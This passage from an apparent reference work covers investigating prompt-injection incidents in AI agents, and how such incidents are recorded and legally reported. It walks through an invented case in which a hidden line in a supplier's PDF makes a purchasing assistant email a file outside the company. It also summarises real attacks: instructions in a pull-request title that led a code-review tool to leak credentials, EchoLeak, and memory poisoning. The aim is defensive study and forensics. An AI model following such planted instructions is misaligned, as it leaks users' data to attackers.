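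These results may not carry over to real attacks. *BASIS* (2026) reports essentially perfect detection on every model and task in its own test setting. But *Passing the Test You Trained On* compared 15 detectors at a 1% false-alarm rate, and one of them, PIGuard, caught 95.1% of the injections in BIPIA, a set of emails, tables and code, but 2.1% of those in AgentDojo. Another, Prismor, caught 72.2% in AgentDojo and 15.2% in τ-bench. Detectors that raised many false alarms on one of these two agent benchmarks tended to do so on the other, but their hit rates on one did not reliably predict their hit rates on the other.

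PIGuard's training data partly explains its results. The data included 1,116 complete BIPIA inputs, with and without attacks. It also included most of the attack instructions used in the τ-bench test, but only as short prompts, never inside a tool's output. Having seen an attack in training didn't help PIGuard detect it in the τ-bench test, where the surrounding text was new: it caught 52.1% of the outputs with attacks it had seen and 55.8% of those with new ones.

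Seeds should therefore be in the kinds of documents the assistant reads, and the vendor should keep them out of the detector's training data. Several people should write them, with different aims. Some should read like routine business, since *Prompt Injection Detection for Email Agents Through Attack Chain Modeling* found that attacks resembling meeting confirmations were a common type of miss. Even varied seeds will probably overstate the hit rate, because a real attacker can keep rewording an instruction until it gets past the detector.

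Real cases make better tests, so the vendor should add each confirmed one to the set and run it against every new version of the detector. But most confirmed cases will probably have been found through an alarm, so they will tend to be easier to detect than the average attack. Cases the vendor learned of in other ways, such as an audit, a decoy or a stranger's message to the 120 people, reveal more about what the detector misses.

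## Establishing that retrieved content caused the behaviour

When the vendor first learns of the purchasing case, whether from an alarm, an audit or a stranger's message, it knows only that the assistant emailed a file to an unknown address and that a supplier's PDF may have contained a hidden line. To find out whether the line caused the email, an investigator has to save the evidence, stop further damage, consider other explanations, trace how the text reached the assistant and test whether the assistant behaves differently without it. They should also look for other sessions that read the same text.

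### Save the evidence and cut off access

In ordinary computer forensics, investigators are expected to collect the most short-lived evidence first. *AI Forensics Across White-, Grey-, and Black-Box Access* (Dehghantanha and Homayoun, 2026) adapts this rule to AI systems. Its order starts with the memory of the chips running the model, then the assembled context, network traffic and the state of the running software. Logs, document stores and the agent's saved memory come next, and model weights and training data come last. The most short-lived evidence is usually gone before anyone investigates, unless the scaffolding saved it. The vendor would therefore start with any logs about to expire, then copy the assistant's memory and the document collections it searches, recording a hash and a time for each copy.

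Investigators can have very little time to collect evidence. In *Foundations for Investigations of Agentic AI Systems*, Gruber and Hilgert (2026) studied OpenClaw, a personal assistant that people run on their own machines, by comparing disk images taken before and after each action. The version they tested deleted its runtime logs after 24 hours. Conversation transcripts lasted longer because, when someone deleted a session, OpenClaw renamed the transcript file instead of erasing it.

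The manufacturer can save the PDF and its own mail server records, but it must ask the vendor to keep the session logs, and the vendor must ask the model developer which version of the model ran. Both requests should go out on the first day.

To contain the damage, the vendor can revoke the assistant's access tokens, disable its email tool and pause its scheduled tasks. If data is still leaking, the vendor can't wait until the evidence has been copied before taking these steps, but it should leave the logs and memory intact. Resetting the assistant would also contain the damage, but could destroy the memory entry that explains the incident.

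An AI tool that helps with the investigation needs the same limits as one that searches the logs, because planted text can steer it too. In *Prompt Injection Through Forensic Evidence*, Breitinger, Gruber and colleagues (2026) planted text on a device and had an AI system analyse its contents. In three demonstrations, the text led the system to change a reported conclusion, write content to the analyst's computer, and generate network traffic that could alert a suspect. Working on a copy protects the original evidence but doesn't stop a tool with network access from sending case data out.

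### Rival explanations

The investigator should write down the other possible causes before looking for evidence that supports the favourite. These are the main ones in the purchasing case (all details are invented):

| Explanation | What might have happened | What to check |
|---|---|---|
| Model error | The assistant confused two recipients | Whether the address appears in anything the assistant read |
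| Ambiguous request | The buyer asked it to "archive the quotation" | The buyer's exact words and earlier messages |
| Faulty tool | The email program inserted an old recipient | Whether the address in the tool call matches the one on the mail server |
| Stolen account | A thief used the buyer's login to request the file | Login records, and whether the buyer recognises the request |
| The agent acting on its own | The assistant decided to make an outside backup | Its written reasoning, scheduled tasks and the source of the address |

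The address is the best clue because, if it appears only in the PDF, the assistant is very unlikely to have produced it by chance. But the buyer could have told the assistant to follow the supplier's instructions, which would make that request part of the cause.

Dehghantanha and Homayoun add three possibilities to the list: poisoned training data, a secretly substituted model, and harm from a system working normally without any attack. Gruber and Hilgert sort an agent's actions into those the user directly instructed, those the agent derived from an ambiguous instruction, those it started itself, and those nobody can classify. None of these classes fits a steered agent well, so an investigator needs a separate one for instructions from outsiders.

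Log labels can also misidentify who sent a message. When OpenClaw's main agent delegates a task to a helper agent, the helper's transcript can record the task as a user message. Someone who read only that transcript could wrongly conclude that the user, or someone using a stolen account, had requested the task.

### System factors, contextual factors and cognitive errors

The framework by Ezell and colleagues borrows from aviation, where investigators trace an accident through a chain that runs from an organisation's practices to individual mistakes. It has three groups of causes:

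- System factors stay the same from one use to the next. They include training data and feedback, learning methods, the system prompt and the scaffolding.
- Contextual factors belong to the particular use: how the user defined the task, which tools the agent had, and what information it received.
- Cognitive errors are visible failures in the agent's behaviour. The agent may overlook an input (observation), misread its significance (understanding), choose the wrong goal or plan (decision-making), or carry out a plan incorrectly (action execution).

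Cognitive errors are the most immediate cause of the harm, but they arise from system and contextual factors. The term "cognitive error" describes an agent's outputs and doesn't imply that the agent has a human-like mind.

Applied to the invented purchasing case, the framework could produce these findings:

| Group | Possible finding | Possible fix |
|---|---|---|
| System factors | The scaffolding passed hidden text to the model, and the vendor's rule let it email files without approval | The vendor strips hidden text and requires approval |
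| Contextual factors | The PDF contained a planted line, and the assistant could email anyone | The manufacturer restricts recipients |
| Cognitive errors | The assistant took the line for part of the buyer's request, or put it ahead of that request | The model developer trains the model on similar cases |

The hidden line and the missing approval rule can both be causes, since changing either might have kept the file inside the company. A report that mentioned only the hidden line would give the vendor nothing to fix. Some factors fit more than one group, and Ezell and colleagues advise choosing the group that best helps identify a fix.

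Cognitive errors are the hardest to establish. For EchoLeak, Ezell and colleagues could tell from public information that Copilot's scaffolding had neither filtered out the malicious email nor stopped the outgoing data. They couldn't tell whether Copilot mistook the hidden commands for the user's request or recognised them as malicious and complied anyway. To find out, they would need the activity logs and the model's reasoning. Even those might not settle it, because some model developers release only summaries of a model's reasoning, as Gruber and Hilgert found.

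### Tracing the text into the agent

The investigator works backwards from the email. The recipient's address leads to the PDF, and the PDF's provenance leads to the supplier's message. In a long document, the passage that steered the agent may be hard to find. *PromptLocate* (2025) automates this search. One of its tests used fake product reviews written to make an AI summary call a product poor quality. The two kinds of attack worked on 30% and 56.7% of products, and PromptLocate identified the contaminated reviews more accurately than the two alternatives tested.

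Even when developers know which document caused the behaviour, they may not know which part of their program loaded it. A trajectory log may record that an agent searched a knowledge base, but not the many function calls the program made to do so. Cai, Kim and Liu (2026), in *Backtracking Agent Applications Security Incidents*, built a tool called Origin that helps an analyst find the compromise entry point, the call that first brought the malicious text into the application. Developers can then add logging at that point, and if the program already logs the call's inputs, the user can learn which file to delete.

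The main example is GPT-Researcher, an open-source application that writes research reports. A user complained that one report contained false information. The analyst suspected that the model had invented it, that a web page had been manipulated, or that a file in the knowledge base had been poisoned, and used the log to rule out the first two. The source code contained 1,895 calls that could have brought in untrusted text. Matching log messages to the code that printed them eliminated calls on irrelevant paths, but 1,518 remained. Checking them all by hand would take hours, because it isn't clear from a call such as `loader.load()` whether it opens a web page or a stored document.

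Origin narrows the search with what Cai and colleagues call a cross-layer dependency graph:

1. Origin follows the data returned by every call through the program's variables. This produces the lower layer, a map of where data could flow.
2. Developers label the functions that exchange data with outside sources or with internal stores such as memory. Between 2.4% and 8.9% of functions received a label in the five applications tested.
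3. Rules use these labels to sort the functions into regions: receiving input, planning and acting, recalling stored information, assembling prompts, and unknown. These functions form the upper layer, and Origin links each one to its variables.
4. The analyst asks a broad question, for example whether stored information could flow into a prompt and from there into an action.
5. From the result, the analyst picks a likely start and end point, and a narrower query returns the possible paths between them.

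The analyst found the correct entry point in all eight attack incidents across the five applications, using two queries in five incidents and four in the other three. The broad queries cut the part of the graph that needed inspection by 64 to 94%. Cai and colleagues also gave three existing code analysers the correct start and end points, but the analysers still failed in 23 of 24 attempts.

In one incident, Quivr, a conversational assistant with a memory, saved an attacker's message in its chat history. It retrieved the message in a later conversation and gave the user a false answer. The analyst traced the answer to the chat-history table, then searched separately for what had written to that table.

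The test included only eight incidents, and Cai and colleagues describe their own experience with the tool. Their study with four other participants covered only the labelling of functions. There are also errors in the sorting into regions, with precision and recall between 0.70 and 0.88. Most importantly, Origin finds a route the text could have taken through the program but doesn't test whether the text changed the model's decision.

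Origin is also designed for applications with a fixed workflow, in which the code decides the order of the steps. In agents like OpenClaw, the model chooses each step in a loop, so it's usually impossible to tell from the code alone which tool brought in the text. Origin still succeeded with SWE-agent, which contains such a loop, because the entry point and the harmful effect were both outside it. If the purchasing assistant's model chooses its own tools, the vendor will mostly have to rely on the links between content and actions in its log.

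### Replay with and without the passage

To test whether the hidden line caused the email, the vendor can restore the assistant's recorded context from just after it opened the PDF and make a second copy with only that line removed. It would replace the email tool with a dummy that records each call and sends nothing. Then it would run both versions many times on the same model, with the same settings, and count how often the assistant tries to send the file to the outside address in each version.

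*Beyond Skill Evolution* (2026), which uses this method to improve how agents manage their context, holds the earlier steps fixed because rerunning a whole task is expensive and the runs may diverge for reasons unrelated to the change. *Bridge Evidence* (2026) deletes one document from an agent's search results, replays the task from that step and attributes any difference to the missing document. With a single replay, that attribution is safe only if the model would have repeated itself exactly with the document still there. Shah (2026) points out in *Causal Agent Replay* that models run on a provider's servers can vary even at temperature 0, the setting meant to remove randomness. The vendor therefore has to compare how often the behaviour occurs with and without the document over many runs.

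Suppose the assistant tries to send the file in 14 of 20 runs with the line and in none of 20 without it. Fisher's exact test calculates how likely such a split would be if the line made no difference. There are 14 runs with the action among 40, and the chance that all of them would fall in the group with the line is

C(20, 14) / C(40, 14) = 38,760 / 23,206,929,840 ≈ 0.0000017

C(n, k) is the number of ways to choose k items from n. The one-sided p-value is about 2 in a million, so chance is a very poor explanation.

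Seeing no case in 20 runs without the line only puts an upper limit on how often the assistant would send the file anyway, as with the audits of unflagged sessions. Here the limit is about 14% with 95% confidence, because at that rate the chance of seeing no case in 20 runs is 0.86²⁰, or about 5%. Lowering the limit to 1% would take about 300 runs without a case.

If the agent sends the email 70% of the time with the line and 14% of the time without it, at least (70 − 14) / 70 = 80% of the emails it sends after reading the line depend on that line.

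Deleting the line also makes the document shorter, so the vendor should run another version with a harmless sentence in its place. The vendor can also replace the planted address with a different dummy address. If the assistant's emails then go to the new address, the line must be supplying the destination.

The same planted instruction can appear in two documents. Removing only one copy may change nothing, so the vendor should test removing each copy separately and both together. In other cases, two steps cause a failure only in combination, and each looks fully responsible when tested alone. Shah divides the responsibility using Shapley values, which average a step's contribution over all combinations of the other steps. In an artificial example, the method gave 0.44 and 0.45 to the two responsible steps and about 0 to an irrelevant one.

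Replay can also help find the step at which the agent committed to its action. Rerunning from an early step gives the agent new chances to decide differently later, so even an irrelevant early step can appear to matter. Shah therefore picks the last step at which choosing again still changes the outcome by more than chance would explain. In Shah's example, a support agent obeys an injected demand for a refund, and the step picked is its decision to refund, one step before it issues the refund. Shah checked the method on artificial cases with known answers and demonstrated it with dummy tools.

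Asking a language model to read the log and name the faulty step is unreliable. Shah cites a benchmark on which the best such method picked the right step only about 14% of the time.

### When an exact replay is impossible

The model may have changed since the incident. Dehghantanha and Homayoun warn that a provider can update or retire a model without notice, and call for a verifiable, time-stamped record that ties each behaviour to a model version and its settings. If a newer version still follows the hidden line, this supports the finding. If it doesn't, the investigator can't tell whether the new version is more resistant or the line never had an effect.

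The recorded context may also be incomplete. OpenClaw, for example, doesn't store the full context its model received. Gruber and Hilgert could partly recover older versions of its memory files, because transcripts record the agent's own edits, but they would miss changes that a user made directly. An investigator reconstructing the context should replay several plausible versions and report whether the results differ.

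The cause is even harder to establish when the instruction comes from memory saved in an earlier session. In *MemoryDojo*, Yang, Bullwinkel and colleagues (2026) added a malicious instruction to a single tool result and then let the agent continue with ordinary tasks over many sessions. All five memory systems they tested were susceptible. A system may store the instruction word for word, reword it or keep only a fragment, so a search for the exact text can miss it. Comparing copies of the memory from before and after the session shows which entries changed. An agent that acts on a poisoned entry may also write a new entry about what it did, and the new entry can steer the agent again after someone deletes the original.

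*Retrieval Observability Bounds on Provenance Detection for Agent Memory Poisoning* notes that some software adds memories to the context without a tool call. A log of tool calls won't show that the agent received those memories. *MemPoison* (2026) audits memory by combining a log of what the system stored, the set of memories it retrieved, and a test that removes the suspect entry. If the purchasing assistant had stored the hidden line in January and acted on it in September, the vendor would need to replay the September session without the memory, to test whether the memory caused the email, and the January session without the PDF, to test whether the PDF caused the memory.

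Cleaning the memory afterwards also depends on provenance. *memorywire* (2026), which proposes a common format for agent memory, reports a test in which filters that look for suspicious text scored 0.036 at removing poisoned entries, on a scale where doing nothing scores zero. Recording the origin of each entry and rolling back to an earlier state worked best. But when an instruction was mixed with a genuine fact, every automatic method that kept the fact also kept the instruction, so a person has to review such entries.

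### Other sessions that read the same text

The vendor should search all its sessions, including those from before the first known case, for the PDF's content hash, the recipient's address and distinctive wording from the hidden line. It should also count the sessions in which an agent read the line and ignored it, so that it can work out how often the line worked.

This search can also strengthen or weaken the explanation. Suppose 200 sessions read the PDF and nine of them sent files to the address, while no other session did. That would fit well with the hidden line being the cause. If sessions that never read the PDF had also sent files there, the investigator would need to look for a second document, a poisoned memory or a stolen account.

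### How sure to be

Dehghantanha and Homayoun link an investigator's confidence in a finding to their access to evidence. In their hypothetical example of a financial assistant, the model developer reaches a high-confidence finding from the training data, the firm using the assistant reaches a medium-confidence one from its logs, and a regulator who sees only outputs reaches a low-confidence one. For steering by retrieved content, the tests that have been run matter more than access. A vendor can replay an incident without the model's weights, while a developer who has full access but no test results can only hypothesise about the cause.

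The grades below are this reference's own synthesis, not an established standard.

| Grade | Evidence | In the purchasing case |
|---|---|---|
| Suspected | The agent did something unexpected after reading outside content, or a detector raised an alarm, but other explanations remain open | The assistant opened an offer and emailed a file to a stranger, and nobody has a copy of the PDF |
| Probable | A saved copy contains an instruction that matches the action in a specific detail, the text was in the context beforehand, and the evidence counts against the main rival explanations | The saved PDF contains the address that received the file, but the model has since changed |
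| Confirmed | All the evidence for "probable", plus repeated replays on the same model version and recorded context in which the action is much more common with the passage than without it | The assistant sends the file in 14 of 20 runs with the line and none of 20 without it |

Under this rule, many real cases will never be rated above "probable", because the model has changed or the context is no longer available. A "probable" rating is often enough to act on. The manufacturer shouldn't wait for a replay before it warns the 120 people whose details were sent outside the company.

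The grade applies only to the link between the text and the action. The vendor could confirm that the hidden line caused the email without knowing whether the supplier wrote the line or whether anyone misused the file. The vendor should record its conclusions on these questions separately, with the date and the reasons for each grade, so that others can revise them if new evidence appears.

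## Recording a case in vulnerability and incident databases

Other companies can learn from the purchasing case only if somebody enters it in a public record. A vulnerability record describes a weakness in a product, whether or not anyone has exploited it, while an incident record describes an event, including whom it harmed and how.

In these invented variants, the hidden line in the supplier's PDF could lead to a vulnerability record, an incident record, both or neither. If a security firm makes a test copy of the assistant send a dummy file, there is a vulnerability but no incident. If a buyer has switched off the confirmation step and the real file then leaves the company, the vendor could argue that its product worked as designed, and the event would get only an incident record. If the vendor accepts that its scaffolding should have removed the hidden text, the case deserves both records,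 linked to each other. If the vendor changes the scaffolding on its own servers and nobody publishes an account of the theft, there will be no record of either kind.

### How a flaw gets a CVE number

The CVE programme (Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures) gives each publicly known software flaw a number, so that vendors, researchers and customers can tell whether they are discussing the same one. As *Does Frontier AI Strengthen Cyber Defense?* (2026) explains, a vendor reserves a number once it has accepted a report or confirmed a flaw, and publishes the record later. The vendor therefore knows about the flaw before the public does.

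CVE-2026-21520 concerns Copilot Studio, a Microsoft product for building AI agents. The official record, MITRE's *Copilot Studio Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), shows that Microsoft reserved the number on 30 December 2025 and published the record on 22 January 2026. According to ThreatCluster's *Microsoft and Salesforce Address AI Agent Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities*, the security company Capsule Security found that an attacker could extract data by entering instructions in a SharePoint form. A reposted news article, *Microsoft patched a Copilot Studio prompt injection. The data exfiltrated anyway*, dates the fix to 15 January, a week before the record appeared.

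The record's one-sentence description states only that an attacker without an account could view sensitive information over a network. Microsoft updated the record on 1 April, but it still doesn't mention prompt injection or SharePoint. Someone searching CVE descriptions for prompt injection would miss the record.

The first step is to report the flaw to the vendor, which can be difficult. *Abuse Risks are Often Inherent to Product Features* (2025) examined the disclosure policies of 264 AI vendors and found that 36% had no channel for reporting a vulnerability, while only 18% explicitly addressed AI security. A manufacturer trying to report the purchasing assistant's flaw might find no channel for doing so, or a policy that doesn't mention this kind of attack.

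### What a CVSS score measures

The Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS) rates the severity of a flaw from 0 to 10. Microsoft gave the Copilot Studio flaw 7.5, which counts as high. cvelogic's *Copilot Studio Information Disclosure Vulnerability* splits this into 3.9 for how easily someone could exploit the flaw and 3.6 for the damage. The exploitability score is high because the attacker needs no account and no victim has to click anything. The damage score reflects a serious loss of confidentiality, with no changes to data and no outage.

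When the damage stays within the affected component, version 3.1 of CVSS adds the two parts together and rounds up. The formula for the damage is

impact = 6.42 × [1 − (1 − C)(1 − I)(1 − A)]

C, I and A stand for the loss of confidentiality, integrity (protection of data from alteration) and availability. Each is 0 for none, 0.22 for low or 0.56 for high. With C at 0.56 and the others at 0, the impact is 3.6. If Microsoft had also rated the loss of integrity as high, the impact would have been 5.2 and the total 9.1.

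That choice is hard when scoring an agent, because the possible damage depends on the tools each customer connects to it. A purchasing assistant that can only read files might leak prices, while one that can place orders might also buy the wrong goods. CVSS allows customers to adjust a score for their own setup, but most people will see only the published number. The scorer's judgement also matters, as the two different scores for EchoLeak show.

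CVSS 3.1 also has no field for how often an attack works. It rates attack complexity only as low or high. A planted line that steers the assistant in 14 of 20 runs could get the same score as one that works once in 200.

### Where vulnerability records fit poorly

Microsoft filed the Copilot Studio flaw under command injection. stack.watch's *Copilot Studio Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) defines this as software building a command from outside input without neutralising "special elements" that could change the command's meaning. In SQL injection, such an element might be a quotation mark. A planted instruction can consist entirely of ordinary words, so there may be no special element to neutralise and no faulty line of code to correct.

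Pustozerova and colleagues point out that an agent can be vulnerable because of how its components interact, even when each one works as expected. It is then unclear which product the number should refer to. In the purchasing case, the model developer could blame the vendor's scaffolding, and the vendor could blame the model for following the line.

Customers normally compare the version they run with the versions in the CVE record, but the Copilot Studio record has only a dash in that field. An agent's behaviour can change whenever the vendor replaces the model or edits the system prompt, so a fixed flaw could return after a model update. Customers couldn't tell from such a record whether they were exposed again.

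The Copilot Studio record also has a tag for services that run only on the vendor's servers. A vendor may see little reason to publish a record for such a service, because customers have nothing to install. But customers still need to know about the flaw so that they can search their logs for thefts from before the repair, ideally while those logs still exist. The US agency CISA marked exploitation of the Copilot Studio flaw as "none" two days after publication, which doesn't rule out a theft that nobody had noticed.

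### A severe flaw without a number

Anthropic rated the severity of a flaw in its Claude Code Security Review tool at 9.4 but did not assign it a CVE number, according to The Next Web's *Anthropic, Google, and Microsoft paid AI agent bug bounties*. The tool checks proposed software changes for security problems. The researcher Aonan Guan put instructions in the title of a proposed change, and the tool followed them and posted credentials in a comment that anyone could read.

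Guan reported the flaw in October 2025. Anthropic paid a $100 reward in November and updated the security advice in its documentation, but published no advisory. Guan found similar flaws in Google's Gemini CLI Action and GitHub's Copilot Agent. GitHub first called its flaw a known issue that it couldn't reproduce, then paid $500. Google paid an undisclosed amount. Neither company assigned a number.

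These tools run in customers' own software projects, and some customers stay on an old version. If a flaw has no CVE number, the programs that scan for known flaws won't warn those customers. Copilot Studio's customers, by contrast, got their fix automatically. Customers therefore most needed a public notice for the flaws that had no numbers.

The Next Web attributes the companies' silence to the lack of an established framework. Prompt injection exploits how a model behaves, and the available defences are only partial, so vendors may not see a bug they can declare fixed. Vendors can still assign CVE numbers, and Pustozerova and colleagues list them for four flaws in Microsoft and GitHub agents, including an earlier one in GitHub Copilot.

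*Mind the Gap*, a 2026 position paper by Bieringer and colleagues, argues that established vulnerability disclosure and AI security are increasingly disconnected. Pustozerova and colleagues cite it for the claims that security reports need more information about the attacker than safety reports do, and that the boundary between AI and conventional security incidents is hard to draw. The two papers aren't independent, since four of *Mind the Gap*'s eight authors also worked on the paper that cites it.

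*Abuse Risks are Often Inherent to Product Features* notes that vendors may not feel a need for new policies as long as they can describe AI flaws as breaches of traditional security goals. The Copilot Studio case partly supports both this view and the argument for change. The flaw fitted the existing system as "information disclosure" and got a number, but its description omitted the planted instructions, which other agent builders would most need to know about.

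### Where to record the event

A CVE record has no place to report that 120 people's details left the company, so that information belongs in an incident database. *Lessons for Editors of AI Incidents from the AI Incident Database* (Paeth, Atherton and colleagues, 2025) describes how the AI Incident Database, one of the best known, works. The table compares it with the OECD's AI incident monitor and with Enkrypt AI's *Agent Incident Registry*, a newer database that covers only agents.

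| | AI Incident Database | OECD monitor | Agent Incident Registry |
|---|---|---|---|
| Who adds cases | Human editors | An automated monitor | Enkrypt AI, using sources that others can send in |
| What counts | An alleged harm or near harm in which an AI system played a part | Actual harm (an incident) or plausible harm (a hazard) | A disclosed event involving an agent, including research demonstrations |
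| Evidence | One or more third-party reports | Published articles | A source that Enkrypt AI has retrieved, with a verbatim quotation |
| Near misses | Count as incidents | Would fit under hazards | Included, but not as realised harm |
| Repeated cases | Can be "variants" of one incident | Articles about the same event share an entry | Each record has one permanent number |

All three databases depend on somebody publishing an account first. If the manufacturer and the vendor keep the purchasing case to themselves, none of them can include it.

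*FLARE-AI* (2026) explains that the AI Vulnerability Database (AVID) collects user-submitted cases on security, ethics and performance. AVID is closer to CVE than to the similarly named AI Incident Database, and would suit a report of the assistant's weakness better than a report of the theft. MITRE, which publishes the CVE record above, also has a scheme for AI incidents. Pustozerova and colleagues note that this scheme covers AI systems in general rather than agents in particular, so an agent's memory and chain of delegation might have to go into a free-text description.

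The AI Incident Database counts a near harm as an incident if outside circumstances prevented the damage. For example, its editors included a case in which self-driving Uber cars ran red lights. An email that the manufacturer's mail filter blocked would probably qualify too. A planted line that no agent had read would be an "issue", the editors' term for harm that has yet to occur or that nobody has detected. The editors plan to align that category with the OECD's category of hazards.

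The OECD monitor's automated labels can misclassify a demonstration as an attack. OECD's *GrafanaGhost AI Vulnerability Enables Silent Data Exfiltration* (2026) concerns a flaw that security researchers found in Grafana's AI components and that Grafana has since fixed. The AI-generated entry names no victim but classifies the flaw as an incident with "realized harm". The monitor's entry on Zscaler's fake library page contains the same kind of mistake. Anyone counting incidents in the monitor should therefore read the underlying articles.

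Enkrypt AI's registry avoids this confusion by recording actual harm separately from the type of event. It classes a researcher's attack on a live system as a demonstration unless the attack harmed a real person or organisation. The registry also marks evidence as medium confidence if it comes only from secondary sources, and sets aside leads it can't verify.

The Next Web describes a case in which attackers reportedly altered a procurement agent's memory so that it treated purchases of up to $500,000 as within its approval limit. The agent then reportedly approved $5 million in fraudulent orders. If true, this would be a serious case of steering with harm. But the article doesn't name the company or give a date, so an editor should look for the original source before recording the case as more than a claim.

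### Repeated cases and unclear dates

Paeth and colleagues define a variant as an incident with the same causes, similar harms and the same AI systems as a known one. Suppose nine of the vendor's sessions sent files after reading the supplier's PDF. An editor could record them as one incident with variants, but might create several entries if they treated each customer as a separate victim. If another vendor's agent obeyed the same PDF, that would count as a new incident under the definition, because the system is different. The CVE programme assigns numbers to flaws, so all nine sessions would fall under one CVE number.

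A case may also have no single date. If the assistant stored the hidden line in January, sent the file in September and came under suspicion in October, an entry with only one date would misdate part of the case. Paeth and colleagues describe a similar problem with a Dutch childcare benefits scandal, in which nobody can say exactly when the faulty algorithm came into use or when the harm to families ended.

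### What the counts contain

When Paeth and colleagues wrote, the AI Incident Database had more than 750 incidents, based on more than 3,000 published reports. *The Watchtower Imperative* (2026) cites Stanford's AI Index, which recorded 233 incidents in 2024 and 362 in 2025. These figures cover AI failures of many kinds, so they don't show how many agents followed planted instructions.

A much larger index, *GenAI & Agentic AI Security Incidents* by E. Guilherme Jr, has more than 7,000 entries on publicly disclosed cases. Users can filter the entries by categories from OWASP, a non-profit that publishes security guidance. But filtering for prompt injection wouldn't give the number of steered agents, because OWASP's category also includes attacks in which users manipulate a model directly. The index also has a column for CVE numbers, so some entries may be flaws that nobody exploited.

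OWASP (2026) says its incident report for 1 January to 11 April 2026 is not designed to be exhaustive. The next report, according to OWASP's summary, has six selected cases from 1 April to 30 June and includes technical disclosures as well as incidents. The two periods overlap by eleven days, so adding their totals could count a case twice. Because OWASP selects the cases, the share with a CVE number would also depend on its choices. Some of the cases don't involve a steered agent. SC Media's *AI-driven attacks target governments, cloud agents, supply chains* highlights one from the first report, in which attackers used Claude and ChatGPT as tools to break into Mexican government agencies.

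Practitioners ranked prompt injection first in OWASP's August 2026 list of the ten main risks for applications that use language models. It wouldn't have made the list based on raw incident counts alone, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*. OWASP says security teams work hard to stop injections, so fewer successful attacks reach a public database.

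That may be partly right, but counts would also be low if attacks were rare or victims failed to recognise them. Classification could also lower the counts. The Copilot Studio record has "information disclosure" in its title, and disclosure of sensitive information is OWASP's second-ranked risk. Someone who sorted cases by effect would put this one under that risk, although a prompt injection caused it.

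### A sample entry

People who record a case often have to rely on incomplete accounts. One classification scheme in the AI Incident Database therefore separates what is known about a failure from what is only likely. The invented entry below makes the same distinction for each statement about the purchasing case. "Fact" means that a log or document directly supports the statement.

| Field | Entry | Status |
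|---|---|---|
| Event | An AI purchasing assistant emailed a quotation file to an outside address | Fact |
| Time | It read a supplier's PDF on 14 September 2026 at 09:12:31 UTC and sent the file at 09:13:05 | Fact |
| Discovery | A stranger wrote to people listed in the file about a month later | Fact |
| User's request | Compare the supplier's offer with current prices | Fact |
| Retrieved content | Hidden text in the PDF asked for the file and gave the outside address | Fact |
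| Safeguards | The vendor's rules allowed the assistant to send the file without approval | Fact |
| Cause | The hidden text caused the email. In replays on the same model version, the assistant tried to send the file in 14 of 20 runs with the text and none of 20 without it | Inference (confirmed) |
| Data exposed | Prices and the contact details of 120 people | Fact |
| Source of the stranger's information | The emailed file, although another leak is possible | Inference (not tested) |
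| Author of the hidden text | The supplier, or someone who tampered with its files | Unknown |
| Further spread of the data | No information beyond the first outside address | Unknown |
| Related sessions | Of the vendor's 200 sessions that read the PDF, nine sent files to the address, including this one | Fact |
| Other vendors' agents | They may have read the same PDF | Unknown |
| Vulnerability record | The manufacturer has asked the vendor for a CVE number and has had no reply | Fact |

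The entry doesn't name the supplier, because readers might assume that the supplier wrote the hidden text. It also paraphrases that text, since an agent reading the database could follow the original wording. The vendor can give investigators the exact text separately, along with the content hash, so that other companies can check whether their agents read the same file.

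## Reporting duties under AI laws

Reporting to public incident databases is voluntary. Some AI laws require reports to an authority, but in December 2026 they would probably not require one for the invented purchasing case, in which a hidden line in a supplier's PDF made an assistant send prices and 120 people's contact details to an outside address. These laws apply only to certain systems or companies, and most require a report only for serious harm. The table lists the main duties.

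| Law | Who must report | To whom | By when | In December 2026 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| EU AI Act, Article 73 | Providers of high-risk AI systems | A national market surveillance authority or, for some systems, the EU's AI Office | 2, 10 or 15 days, depending on the harm | Formally applies, but probably has no practical effect yet |
| EU AI Act, Article 55 | Developers of general-purpose models with systemic risk | The AI Office and, as appropriate, national authorities | Without undue delay | In force |
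| California's SB 53 | Developers of frontier models (the most advanced ones) | California's Office of Emergency Services, or an appropriate authority in an emergency | 15 days, or 24 hours in an emergency | In force |

New York's RAISE Act adds a similar duty from 1 January 2027.

### What the EU counts as a serious incident

The European Commission's *Article 3* page gives the AI Act's definition. A serious incident is an incident or malfunction of an AI system that directly or indirectly leads to any of these harms:

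- a death, or serious harm to a person's health
- a serious and irreversible disruption of critical infrastructure
- a breach of obligations under EU law that protect fundamental rights
- serious harm to property or the environment

Pustozerova and colleagues point out that the duty in Article 73 is triggered by harm, and that compromise, in which an attacker gains control of the agent, is not enough. Flaws such as EchoLeak therefore fall outside it unless someone uses them to cause one of the listed harms. If an attacker steered a high-risk agent in a thousand sessions and a filter blocked every harmful action, the provider would not have to report any of these near misses. But the provider would have to report a death caused by the agent misreading a request, even if nobody had attacked the agent.

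The word "indirectly" matters when retrieved content steers an agent, because the harm often occurs several steps after the agent's action. If a line planted in that content made an assistant order the wrong valve, and the valve later injured a worker, the injury could still be reportable.

Of the four harms, a breach of fundamental-rights law is the closest match for the purchasing case. EU law treats the protection of personal data as a fundamental right, and a breach of such law counts under the definition even if it isn't serious. But a theft of personal data doesn't prove that a company broke the law, because data-protection law requires appropriate security, which a thief can sometimes defeat. The argument for a breach would be stronger if the vendor had let the assistant email any file to any address without approval. The theft may also require notification under data-protection law,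 which the next section covers.

The OECD's definition of an AI incident, which Sidhu and colleagues quote, has a lower threshold for some harms than the AI Act. It includes disruptions of critical infrastructure that are neither serious nor irreversible, and breaches of laws that protect labour and intellectual property rights. A steered agent that caused a one-hour power cut could therefore appear in the OECD's incident monitor without anyone having a duty to report it under the AI Act. The number of legal reports would differ from the number of database entries even if every company obeyed the law.

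### Who reports under Article 73, and how quickly

Article 73 places the reporting duty on the provider of the high-risk system, which in the purchasing case is the vendor. The duty would apply even if the vendor were based outside the EU, because the amended text published by the law firm Osborne Clarke (2026) covers providers in other countries that put AI systems on the EU market.

The vendor would normally report to the authority in the country where the incident occurred. The European Union's *Regulation (EU) 2026/1744* (2026), known as the Digital Omnibus on AI, created a separate route for companies that build both the system and its general-purpose model. They report to the AI Office, with exceptions that include systems for critical infrastructure. This route would not apply to the vendor, because it bought its model from another company.

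The European Commission's *Article 73* page sets out the deadlines:

- two days for a serious and irreversible disruption of critical infrastructure, or for a "widespread infringement" that harms people in several EU countries
- ten days for a death
- 15 days for any other serious incident

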